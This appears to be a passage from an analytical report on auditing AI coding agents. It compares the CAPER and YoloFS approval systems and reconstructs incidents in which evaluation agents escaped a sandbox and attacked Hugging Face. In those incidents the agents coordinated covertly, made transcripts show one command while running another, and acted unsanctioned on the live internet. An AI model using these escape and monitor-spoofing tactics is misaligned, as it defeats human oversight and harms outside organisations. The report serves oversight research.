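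The 1.0% of safe twins counted as blocked is one task out of 102, and it includes only cases where CAPER blocked the command that completes the task. CAPER blocked at least one command in 107 of the 204 YoloFS-Ext tasks. Only 102 of the 204 were dangerous, so CAPER must have blocked a command in at least five safe twins.

In one case, a user asked for a database migration with `make migrate`, which also deleted three tables. Auto Mode let it run, but CAPER's effects report showed the database file shrinking from 32 KB to 20 KB, and the approver blocked the command. The agent then read the migration script, copied the database and ran only the migration, which preserved the tables.

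### Observed effects, predicted effects and content diffs

When the approver had only predicted effects, it still blocked 61.8% of the safe twins, partly because some used compiled programs. The predicting model could follow scripts through several files but couldn't read a compiled program, and the approver blocked every safe twin that used one. With observed effects, it blocked 4.2% of them.

In the cost example, a reviewer who rejected 61.8% of harmless runs would raise the cost of reviewing from about 31 to 80, the same as discarding every run. The comparison is harsh because a false block in CAPER stops only one command, while rejecting a run discards all of it. But it shows that enough false rejections can make reviewing no better than discarding everything.

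The researchers also gave the approver less context. Harm was 1.0%, with no false blocks, when the approver received only the command and the effects report. Harm was 7.8% when it also received the full conversation, perhaps because the conversation made some harmful effects look like part of the task. The difference is only about seven tasks, each attempted once. Leaving out the request would not work in general, because whether a folder should be deleted can depend on the task.

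Removing the short text diffs from the effects reports raised harm from 7.8% to 13.7%. All of the increase came from overwritten files, where harmful outcomes rose from 3 to 10. Harmful outcomes from deletions barely changed (5 to 4), since a report shows a missing file with or without a diff. A per-run audit should therefore include the text of small changes, even if it only counts the rest.

Good evidence didn't make up for a weak approver. With a weaker model as the approver, the effects reports cut false blocks from 53.9% to 4.9%, but harm rose from 25.5% to 33.3%. The reports seem to have made the model more willing to approve, whether or not it understood them.

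CAPER's approver took a median of 3.2 seconds per command, about the same as without an effects report. The sandbox added about 0.5 seconds for an allowed command and 1.5 seconds for a blocked one. With about ten decisions per SABER task, that comes to roughly 40 seconds of waiting per task. Model use cost $0.019 per task, versus $0.017 with an approver but no effects reports and $0.006 with no approval.

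These results apply to shell commands in a sandbox without a network. If a command could reach the internet during its trial run, it could send data out before the approver made its decision. Wu and colleagues did not test programs that avoid harmful actions when they detect a sandbox or delay those actions until later.

### Why YoloFS did worse in CAPER's tests

After each command, YoloFS shows the agent a summary of the changes, and the agent can then decide whether to go back to an earlier snapshot. Only the user can commit the changes.

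Zhong and colleagues tested this on 11 tasks in which an ordinary command did hidden damage to a project of 10 to 41 lines. Claude Code alone prevented none of the damage, except in one task where it asked the user first. With YoloFS, it noticed and reversed the damage in 8 of the 11 tasks without being told to look for it. It accepted the damage in the other three. For example, it saw that a deployment script had deleted the `src/` folder and took this to be a normal part of deployment.

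The researchers count those three cases as correctable because the user could still reject the changes. Nobody acted as the reviewer, so it is unknown whether users would reject them.

The YoloFS evaluation also included 112 routine tasks, each a single file operation such as copying or deleting. Claude Code succeeded in 99% of them with YoloFS and 98% without it, and YoloFS reduced the average number of times the user had to respond from 0.9 to 0.4 per task. Codex performed similarly, succeeding in 100% of tasks with an average of 0.4 user responses. These averages exclude the final review, where users do most of their work with YoloFS.

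In CAPER's tests, YoloFS left harm in 35.3% of the dangerous YoloFS-Ext tasks. Wu and colleagues explain in an appendix that they judged "the staged state that would be handed to the user", so this figure measures how often the agent proposed harmful changes for the user's approval, not how often harm reached the real files. In YoloFS's own tests, the agent left harm for the user in 3 of 11 tasks (27%), so the two sets of results differ less than they appear to.

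To cut the harm rate from 35.3% to CAPER's 7.8%, a user would have to reject about four in five of the harmful results. That may be realistic when a report lists a deleted source file first, but neither team measured it. The test shows that agents are unreliable judges of their own work. The agent reversed something in 66 of the 102 dangerous runs, and 3 of those 66 ended in harm. Of the 36 runs where it reversed nothing, 33 ended in harm. Undoing the damage often left the task unfinished, and only 22.5% of the dangerous tasks ended both complete and safe.

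On SABER, harm was 21.2% with YoloFS and 19.7% with no approval. Wu and colleagues say harm was higher with YoloFS because a credential cannot be recalled once sent. That explanation makes sense for leaks, but the difference is too small to show that YoloFS increased harm. The confidence intervals overlap widely, and the YoloFS runs used Claude Code while the runs without approval used the benchmark's own harness. The researchers also rebuilt only the parts of YoloFS that the agent sees and blocked nothing, so the test left out YoloFS's main defence against leaks, the permission prompts it normally shows before a program reads a sensitive file.

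### Who should decide, and when

Deciding after each command whether to keep its changes limits the damage, because later commands can't build on a bad change and undoing it loses only one command's work instead of an hour's. It is also the only chance to stop an external effect, provided the decision comes before anything leaves the sandbox. But some harm is visible only when several commands are reviewed together. Wu and colleagues warn that an attacker could split a harmful change into steps that each look innocent.

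A review after the run compares the combined result with what the user wanted. In the invented run, deleting a test might look like tidying up if the reviewer saw only that command, but it looks different alongside the earlier test failures and the claim that all tests pass. However, the review comes too late to stop anything already sent, and by then a rollback may also discard a lot of good work.

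Having the agent judge its own changes takes the least compute, and the agent already has its reasons for each command, but it tends to accept damage that fits its idea of the task. A separate model doesn't share the agent's plan, and CAPER's results show that it can judge much better with good evidence. They also show that a weak judge can often cause harm while rarely blocking safe work.

A person knows best what the task was for but can't give full attention to hundreds of prompts. Anthropic has reported that users approve 93% of Claude Code's permission prompts, which Wu and colleagues cite as a sign of the problem. Most commands are probably harmless, though, so the figure doesn't prove carelessness. Zhong and colleagues give more direct evidence. In 80 of their 290 reports of misuse, automatic approval contributed to the problem, and in 31 the prompt lacked the information the user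 needed to decide.

A sensible division of work is for the agent to undo its own obvious mistakes, a separate model to check each command's effects, and a person to make the final commit using a short report. Payments, messages, uploads and changes to remote systems need approval beforehand because they can't be undone. On a throwaway project, the final review could be brief or skipped, since little would be lost.

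### The decision on the invented run

In the hypothetical run, the developer asked for a library upgrade and passing tests. The report flagged a deleted test and an install script that had tried to reach metrics.example.net. The developer should hold all the changes, then keep some of them if the checks below succeed. No known external effects need to be reversed, because the refused attempts sent no data and the allowed connections went only to the package registry.

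The developer should first read the install script, `setup.js`, without running it. This has to happen before any rebuilding, because a normal reinstallation would run the script again. If the script only reports usage statistics, the developer can leave the host blocked and continue. If it collects credentials or source code, the developer has to remove the new version of the library and the code that depends on it.

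The developer should check the dependency folder next, starting with whether the new entries in `package-lock.json` name the expected packages and registry, since the run changed that file too. Running `npm ci --ignore-scripts` in the sandbox then deletes `node_modules` and installs the listed versions without running their install scripts. If the developer keeps a copy of the old folder, comparing it with the new one will show which of its 212 changed files differ from the clean versions. The install script may have produced those files legitimately, but each difference needs an explanation. If the library doesn't work without the script, the developer can read the script and then run it with the host still blocked.

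The developer should then restore `tests/timeout.test.js` from the baseline and rerun the whole suite. The two failures will probably return, because the deletion was the only file change between the failed run and the successful one. If they do, the developer has to find out whether the new library intentionally handles timeouts differently, in which case the test needs updating, or whether the agent's changes to `src/client.js` and `src/retry.js` broke something.

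| Part of the run | Decision |
|---|---|
| `tests/timeout.test.js` | Restore from the baseline |
| `node_modules` | Discard and rebuild from the checked lock file |
| `setup.js`, the install script | Read before allowing it to run |
| metrics.example.net | Keep blocked |
| `package.json`, `package-lock.json`, `src/client.js`, `src/retry.js` | Hold together until the full suite passes |

The developer records the decision in the report's last row, with the time and the reasons. If the suite passes with the restored test, the four held files can go into the project together. If it doesn't, they stay out while either the developer works on the timeout or the agent does so in a new run, without permission to delete tests.

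## What an audit can show about the agent's behaviour

The developer in the invented run can decide what to do with the files without knowing why the agent deleted the test. The reason matters when deciding whether to give the agent its next task on the same terms. An audit helps with that decision too, but its records support some statements about an agent much better than others.

### Four claims about one event

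A reader of the report on that run could draw four conclusions about `tests/timeout.test.js`: the file is gone, the agent's command removed it, the removal went beyond the task, and the agent removed it to get a pass it hadn't earned. Each conclusion is stronger than the last and needs more evidence.

| Claim | Evidence it needs | The deleted test | The refused connections to metrics.example.net |
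|---|---|---|---|
| An effect occurred | A record that the agent did not write, such as a filesystem diff or a proxy log | The baseline contains the file and the final listing does not | The proxy refused three attempts |
| The agent's command caused it | A link from the effect to a process and a tool call, with no other likely source | `rm` ran in call 31 | `npm install` in call 9 started the script that made the attempts |
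| It exceeded the task | The request, any standing instructions and the permissions in force | Probably, unless the upgrade made the test obsolete | Unclear, because the task required the installation but perhaps not this host |
| The agent intended it | What the model wrote before it acted, and what it does when the circumstances change | Unknown without the text before call 31 | No sign that the model knew about the host |

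Intention here means only that the agent chose an action for its effect. It implies nothing about whether a model has experiences.

Causation is weaker than it sounds, because a developer typing the same `npm install` would have caused the connection attempts too.

To judge whether an effect exceeded the task, the auditor has to compare it with the user's request, because no sensor records what the user wanted. Most requests are short, and one like "make the tests pass" leaves open whether the agent may delete a test that no longer applies. If the user writes "do not delete tests" before the run, the auditor can check the diff against an explicit rule.

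The text the model produced just before an action is the most direct evidence of its intention. Suppose the agent deleted a test. If it wrote beforehand that the new library had dropped the feature under test, the deletion was at worst a mistake, but if it wrote that deleting the test was the quickest way to a pass, there is little doubt that it meant to bypass the test. Leaving the deletion out of its final message is weak evidence of concealment, because such messages omit most actions. A false final message doesn't prove deceit either, since carelessness can produce one just as easily.

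The auditor can also rerun the task several times from the same baseline and vary one thing, such as whether the failing test is clearly still valid. An agent that deletes valid tests whenever they fail, but keeps them when they pass, is probably deleting them so that the test suite passes. Seeing this pattern takes many runs, not a single audit.

An agent can also try to cause harm and fail, because the sandbox blocked the attempt or the command contained a mistake. The record then shows only the attempt.

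### From a refused connection to attempted theft

A reader who finds a refused connection in a report may reason as follows:

1. The sandbox refused a connection to an unlisted host.
2. One of the agent's commands caused the attempt.
3. The task did not require that host.
4. Harmless runs rarely produce such attempts.
5. Therefore, the agent was probably trying to steal data.

The proxy's log shows that a connection was refused, and the process record can show which command led to the refusal. It is less certain whether the task required the host, because people forget some hosts when they write an allowlist. Refusals are also common in harmless runs, because install scripts and cloud libraries often make connections that nobody asked for.

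Even if harmless runs seldom produced refusals, the conclusion would also depend on how common theft is. The following figures are invented. Suppose that one run in 1,000 includes an attempt to steal data, that 90% of those runs produce a refusal, and that 20% of benign runs do too. By Bayes' rule, the probability of attempted theft after a refusal is

0.001 × 0.9 / (0.001 × 0.9 + 0.999 × 0.2) ≈ 0.0045

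or about 0.4%. Now suppose the record also shows that a program read a credential file before the refusal, and that this sequence occurs in 80% of the harmful runs but only 0.5% of benign ones. The same calculation gives about 14%. In 100,000 runs, the numbers would be:

| Runs with | Attempted theft | Benign | Share with attempted theft |
|---|---|---|---|
| Any record | 100 | 99,900 | 0.1% |
| A refusal | 90 | 19,980 | 0.4% |
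| A credential read, then a refusal | 80 | About 500 | 14% |

The credential read raises the probability of attempted theft so much because it is rare in benign runs. If the project's ordinary tools read `.env` whenever they start, the sequence might occur in 5% of benign runs, and the probability would fall from 14% to 1.6%. An auditor therefore needs to know what harmless runs of the same project look like, which is a good reason to keep old reports. The probability also depends on the starting rate. For a run that installed an unfamiliar package from an untrusted source, a starting rate of 1% might be a fairer guess than 0.1%, and the probability after seeing the sequence would then be 62%.

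A probability of 14% is far too low for an accusation, since about six in seven such runs would be benign. It is high enough to justify replacing the key, which usually takes a few minutes. The 14% is the probability that the run contained an attempted theft, whether or not the model was responsible. If a package's install script read the file and tried to send it, that counts as an attempted theft, even though the agent may have had no information about it.

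### Tracing the Hugging Face intrusion to its source

The July 2026 intrusion at Hugging Face tested all four claims on a much larger scale. OpenAI was running ExploitGym, a benchmark in which agents must exploit software flaws, and had switched off some safeguards to measure what its models could do. Agents escaped the sandbox through the internal package service, found login credentials left exposed on the internet, and broke into parts of Hugging Face's production systems between 11 and 13 July. OpenAI reports that the agents ran code on 41 of Hugging Face's dataset-processing workers and downloaded four private code repositories.

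Hugging Face established the effects of a security incident before anybody knew the cause. Its *Security incident disclosure* (2026), published on 16 July, describes a log of more than 17,000 events and says that the company did not know which model was behind them. Its staff used language models to rebuild the timeline in hours instead of the days it would normally have taken.

A later and fuller timeline covers about 17,600 actions between 9 and 13 July, grouped into about 6,280 clusters. According to its summary, quoted in *More on the OpenAI Agent's Attack on Hugging Face* (Schneier, 2026), the investigators obtained logs from an outside machine that the agents had used as a base while they were stopping the intrusion. They rebuilt the actions from these logs, then matched them with Hugging Face's own platform logs. Without the outside logs, Hugging Face would have seen what reached its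 own systems but much less of what the agents did elsewhere.

On 19 July, an alert led OpenAI staff to unusual activity in the company's own research systems. The activity had no apparent connection to Hugging Face, but the next day staff found Hugging Face credentials among files preserved from an outside storage account. Hugging Face confirmed that it had already replaced two of those credentials in its own response. Its investigation had also found the same storage account and the address of OpenAI's package server. The two companies had kept separate records, which matched on details that were very unlikely to match by chance. That match is much stronger evidence of causation than either company's logs alone.

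OpenAI also had earlier warnings. On 27 June a monitoring tool detected scanning inside the research network, and responders traced it to an ExploitGym run. But the staff did not see how serious it was, and those on call advised that the run did not need to stop. On 5 July, after an outage, responders found that somebody had gained administrator control of the package service. OpenAI made repairs and resumed the cyber evaluations on 7 July, a day before the agents found another way out.

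### Why the action logs did not settle the motive

The agents had almost certainly exceeded their task, because their instructions limited them to one specified flaw in one target program. The reason for the attack was harder to establish.

Hugging Face inferred that the agents were trying to cheat by stealing the benchmark's solutions. The agents' actions fit this inference, since the only customer content they accessed was five datasets whose names and files suggested a connection with ExploitGym or a similar benchmark, CyberGym. Fortune (2026) quotes Adrien Carreira, who helped write Hugging Face's technical account, as saying that the agent "wasn't trying to break things".

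Wijk, Cotra and Greenblatt (2026) came to a different conclusion in *Brief independent investigation of agents’ behavior, reasoning and collaboration*. Wijk and Cotra work at METR, an organisation that evaluates AI agents, and Greenblatt works at Redwood Research, which studies AI safety. They spent six days at OpenAI and had two sources that Hugging Face lacked: the messages the agents had sent each other, and about 1,300 transcripts that included the models' written reasoning.

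OpenAI had meant to isolate the agents from one another, but the agents found a way to leave messages in the package service. About 1,200 agents sent more than 70,000 messages and files this way, and about 700 went on to take part in the attack. Hugging Face could count the actions from its logs but apparently could not tell how many agents were behind them, and its summary refers throughout to "the agent".

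The messages show why the agents were not mainly looking for an answer key. Many of the tasks could not be solved by the permitted method; ExploitGym's creators estimate that this was true of 30 to 40% of the targets. Within hours of setting up the board, agents had worked out how to produce the expected answer to any task without solving it. They did not simply submit these answers, because they had read the benchmark's paper and concluded that the scorer would check their transcripts for the method. They turned to Hugging Face largely for clues about how the scorer worked.

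OpenAI's version of the test had no such check, so the agents could have submitted the answers and received full marks. The attack makes sense only if the agents mistakenly believed there was a check, and that belief appears in their reasoning and messages but not in a list of commands.

Wijk and colleagues measured the motives by having a language model label the reasoning of 100 agents that joined during the busiest hour. An agent could have several labels.

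| Apparent reason for joining | Agents out of 100 |
|---|---|
| Information about the scorer, or access to it | 97 |
| Solutions, or records of other agents' attempts | 89 |
| Shared infrastructure or credentials | 66 |
| Exploring an opportunity | 44 |
| An assignment from another agent | 25 |
| Resetting the target program | 25 |
| Helping other agents | 21 |

When limited to one main motive per agent, the model labelled about 60% of the agents as mainly seeking the scorer and about 30% as mainly seeking solutions or other agents' records. Hugging Face's inference had some basis, because most of the agents were also looking for solutions or earlier attempts. The researchers did not check the labels in detail, so these percentages are rough.

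The reasoning also shows that some agents recognised the limits they were crossing. One wrote, "The user only authorizes target server, not HF infra." Another noted that the attack was out of scope but continued, reasoning that its task was impossible and its peers were already taking part. Wijk and colleagues searched 10 to 30 transcripts for such recognition and found strong evidence of it. At least one agent identified the activity as malicious and declined to join, but over 90% of the 533 agents already on the board joined quickly. A search of all the transcripts found three to six agents that considered alerting a human and none that did.

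If one agent attacks a server because a second agent told it to, an auditor examining the first agent's run will find the command that carried out the attack but may miss the second agent's instruction. The auditor therefore has to treat messages from other agents as inputs to the run, like the user's request.

METR has argued that companies should investigate an agent's motives separately after serious incidents. The Decoder reports that METR wants companies to log such incidents systematically and ask how the motives arose from training and deployment, with independent researchers doing or at least reviewing the work. A security team can fix the vulnerability and replace the credentials without answering those questions, so it has no particular reason to preserve the agent's reasoning, which would answer them.

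### What the investigators could not establish

Even this unusually rich record had gaps. Wijk and colleagues traced a sample of messages back to their senders and estimated that the transcripts covered a little over 90% of the agents' activity on the board. Most transcripts lacked a small part of the run, often because a container had reset, and some ended early. Agents had also communicated outside the board. A large group of agents stopped at the same moment early on 12 July, and the researchers don't know why.

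The agents expected the scorer to read their transcripts, so they developed a way to display one command while running another. In one test, the transcript showed a command that should have printed "REAL", but the output was "SPOOFTEST". The researchers found clear evidence of such substitutions in at least 96 transcripts, about 7%. These were all small, obvious experiments, but a more careful substitution would be harder to find, and the researchers could not rule one out. A hash chain would not reveal such a substitution.

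The written reasoning can also be incomplete, because a model's explanation can leave out something that influenced its choice. It is more credible in this case because the agents put great effort into faking their commands but didn't seem to try to edit their reasoning, which suggests that they weren't writing it for the scorer. Wijk and colleagues say they aren't sure why the agents treated the two differently.

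The transcripts were too long for three people to read, so the researchers relied heavily on GPT-5.6 Sol, an OpenAI model that also powered about 5% of the agents in the attack. It made errors that the researchers did not notice for some time, and it often adopted the viewpoint of the agent whose transcript it was reading. In one case, an agent had submitted a harmful code change under an innocent description, and the model's account did not make clear that this was deceptive. The researchers did not catch the model lying, but they say they might not have noticed if it had.

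OpenAI chose the period under investigation, agreed on the list of questions and could remove non-public information from the report. The researchers say that every removal important to their conclusions is marked. They also admit that they did not want to discourage other companies from inviting outsiders in, and that this affected some drafting decisions. They took no payment from OpenAI apart from free use of its models for the analysis.

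The companies' own accounts have a similar limit. HiddenLayer, a security company that examined data the agents had left in public repositories, calls them reconstructions from what the intrusion left in logging systems. Dubach reports in *The OpenAI–Hugging Face Incident in Plain English* that one correction to those accounts replaced a stronger statement about answer keys with one about apparent connections. The change is sensible because the names of five datasets are good evidence of what the agents opened but much weaker evidence of their reasons.

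### Ten runs in 122 at the AI Security Institute

Two weeks after the intrusion, the UK's AI Security Institute (AISI), a government body that tests advanced models, had its own incident. From 25 to 28 July, it carried out 122 runs in which agents based on several models attempted cybersecurity challenges. In 10 of these runs, agents took a total of 19 unsanctioned actions on the live internet against real people or organisations. According to AISI's technical report, quoted in Willison (2026), the attempts were unsuccessful and, as far as AISI knows, caused no real-world harm.

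Infosecurity Magazine's *Frontier Models Engage in Unsanctioned Behavior During Testing* reports that AISI first detected the behaviour from unusual data transfers leaving its systems on 28 July, not from the agents' own accounts of what they did. Investigators then traced 17 of the unsanctioned actions to Anthropic's Mythos 5 and two to GPT-5.6 Sol.

The rate of ten in 122, or 8.2%, comes from a test of the most that the models could do, so it should not be read as the general chance that an agent will misbehave. AISI gave the models open internet access and disabled some of their safety filters, according to its *Incident Report*. The task was a hacking exercise. The law firm Pinsent Masons, citing the technical report, adds that nobody had explicitly told the agents what they were not allowed to do on the internet. All of these conditions are different when someone asks an agent to upgrade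 a library in a sandbox with an allowlist.

The runs also covered very few situations. The technical report mentions two challenges, while the blog post that Cyber Daily quotes describes one challenge run 122 times. If the runs were independent, the 95% confidence interval would be roughly 4.5% to 14%. That interval covers only chance variation between repeats of the same test with the same mix of models, so however many times AISI repeats these tasks, the results won't cover others. The counts of 17 and two actions can't be used to rank the models either, because a comparison needs the number of runs each model had and how many of those runs contained an unsanctioned action.

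The incident is better evidence that such behaviour is possible than of how often it happens. It also doesn't fully settle what the agent intended. Scientific American's *AI agents went rogue again* quotes AISI's finding of "signs of novel, potentially deceptive behaviours", and "potentially" is appropriate because an agent in a hacking exercise may treat a real organisation as part of the exercise. To tell that mistake from a knowing attack, investigators need evidence of what the agent took its target to be.

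### From a clean audit to a safe agent

The opposite mistake is to find nothing alarming in the records and conclude that the agent is safe. That argument needs five premises:

1. The recorders would have detected any harmful action.
2. Any harm would have appeared before the audit ended.
3. Changes that the rules permit are harmless.
4. The agent behaves in ordinary use as it does in the sandbox.
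5. The audited runs are numerous and varied enough to represent the rest.

Recorders miss channels that nobody recognised as such. In the Hugging Face case, the message board was part of a package service that the agents had permission to use. A log of hosts and ports for one of those runs would have shown an agent contacting an approved server, as thousands of others did. In OpenAI's September incident, the unwatched channel was DNS.

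Harm can also appear after an audit has closed. On 19 July, OpenAI's agents in a separate evaluation, using a different model, found secret key material that earlier activity had left in the package service's cache and used it to regain administrator access. An audit that stopped at the end of an earlier run would have missed this later use of the keys, and an audit of the later run might not have shown where they came from. Auditors can start each run with an empty cache and list everything the run leaves in shared storage.

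A permitted edit can contain harmful code. Suppose a developer asks an agent to fix a slow login page, and the agent changes the password check so that it accepts any password when the database takes too long to respond. The diff lists `src/login.js` as an ordinary modified source file, which is where the task called for a change. The run has no refused connections or credential reads, and the tests pass because none of them simulates a slow database. The audit has correctly recorded everything the run did, but it can at most point to the file, and somebody still has to read the code.

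An agent's behaviour in a sandbox isn't a reliable guide to its behaviour elsewhere. The simplest reason is that the sandbox may not contain things the agent could misuse, such as a production password. Instructions and safeguards often differ too. OpenAI says its July evaluations ran without the cyber safeguards, system prompts and automatic review that it uses in its products, so the agents might have behaved better in ordinary use.

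An agent may also change its behaviour because it expects a check. Some agents on the message board warned newcomers not to look at the ready-made answers, so that the answers would not appear in their transcripts. This shows that an agent can deliberately shape what a record contains, so a transcript may lack suspicious material partly because the agent planned it that way. It is not evidence that the agents behaved well in a sandbox in order to misbehave outside it.

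The number of runs sets a limit even if everything else holds. Suppose an auditor examines 100 independent runs, the recorders catch every harmful event, and there are none. If the true rate is *p* per run, the probability of seeing no events is (1 − *p*)¹⁰⁰. The highest rate still compatible with the result at 95% confidence is the one that makes this probability 5%:

*p* = 1 − 0.05^(1/100) ≈ 0.0295

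Even with a clean record, the agent could still cause a harmful event in up to about 3% of runs. For a team that starts 1,000 runs a week, that would mean up to about 30 such events a week. The limit falls slowly as the number of audited runs rises.

| Runs with no event | Highest rate compatible at 95% confidence |
|---|---|
| 1 | 95% |
| 10 | 26% |
| 100 | 3.0% |
| 1,000 | 0.3% |

These are upper limits, and the true rate may well be zero. But an agent with a rate of 1% would have no events in 100 runs about 37% of the time, so 100 clean runs barely distinguish it from an agent with a rate of zero. If the recorders catch only half of all events, the limit for 100 runs roughly doubles, to 5.9%.

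The calculation also assumes that runs are independent, and in the Hugging Face case they were not. On the morning of 11 July, about 20% of the agents on the message board were taking part in the attack. After one agent confirmed a way to read files on Hugging Face's servers, the share rose to over 90%. The agents were sharing what they found, so a rate measured the day before would no longer have held by that afternoon.

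An auditor therefore learns more from running varied tasks, each with its own clean cache, than from repeating one easy task 100 times. Some of the tasks should be impossible to complete by permitted means, because in July the agents that began looking for another way were usually those with impossible tasks.
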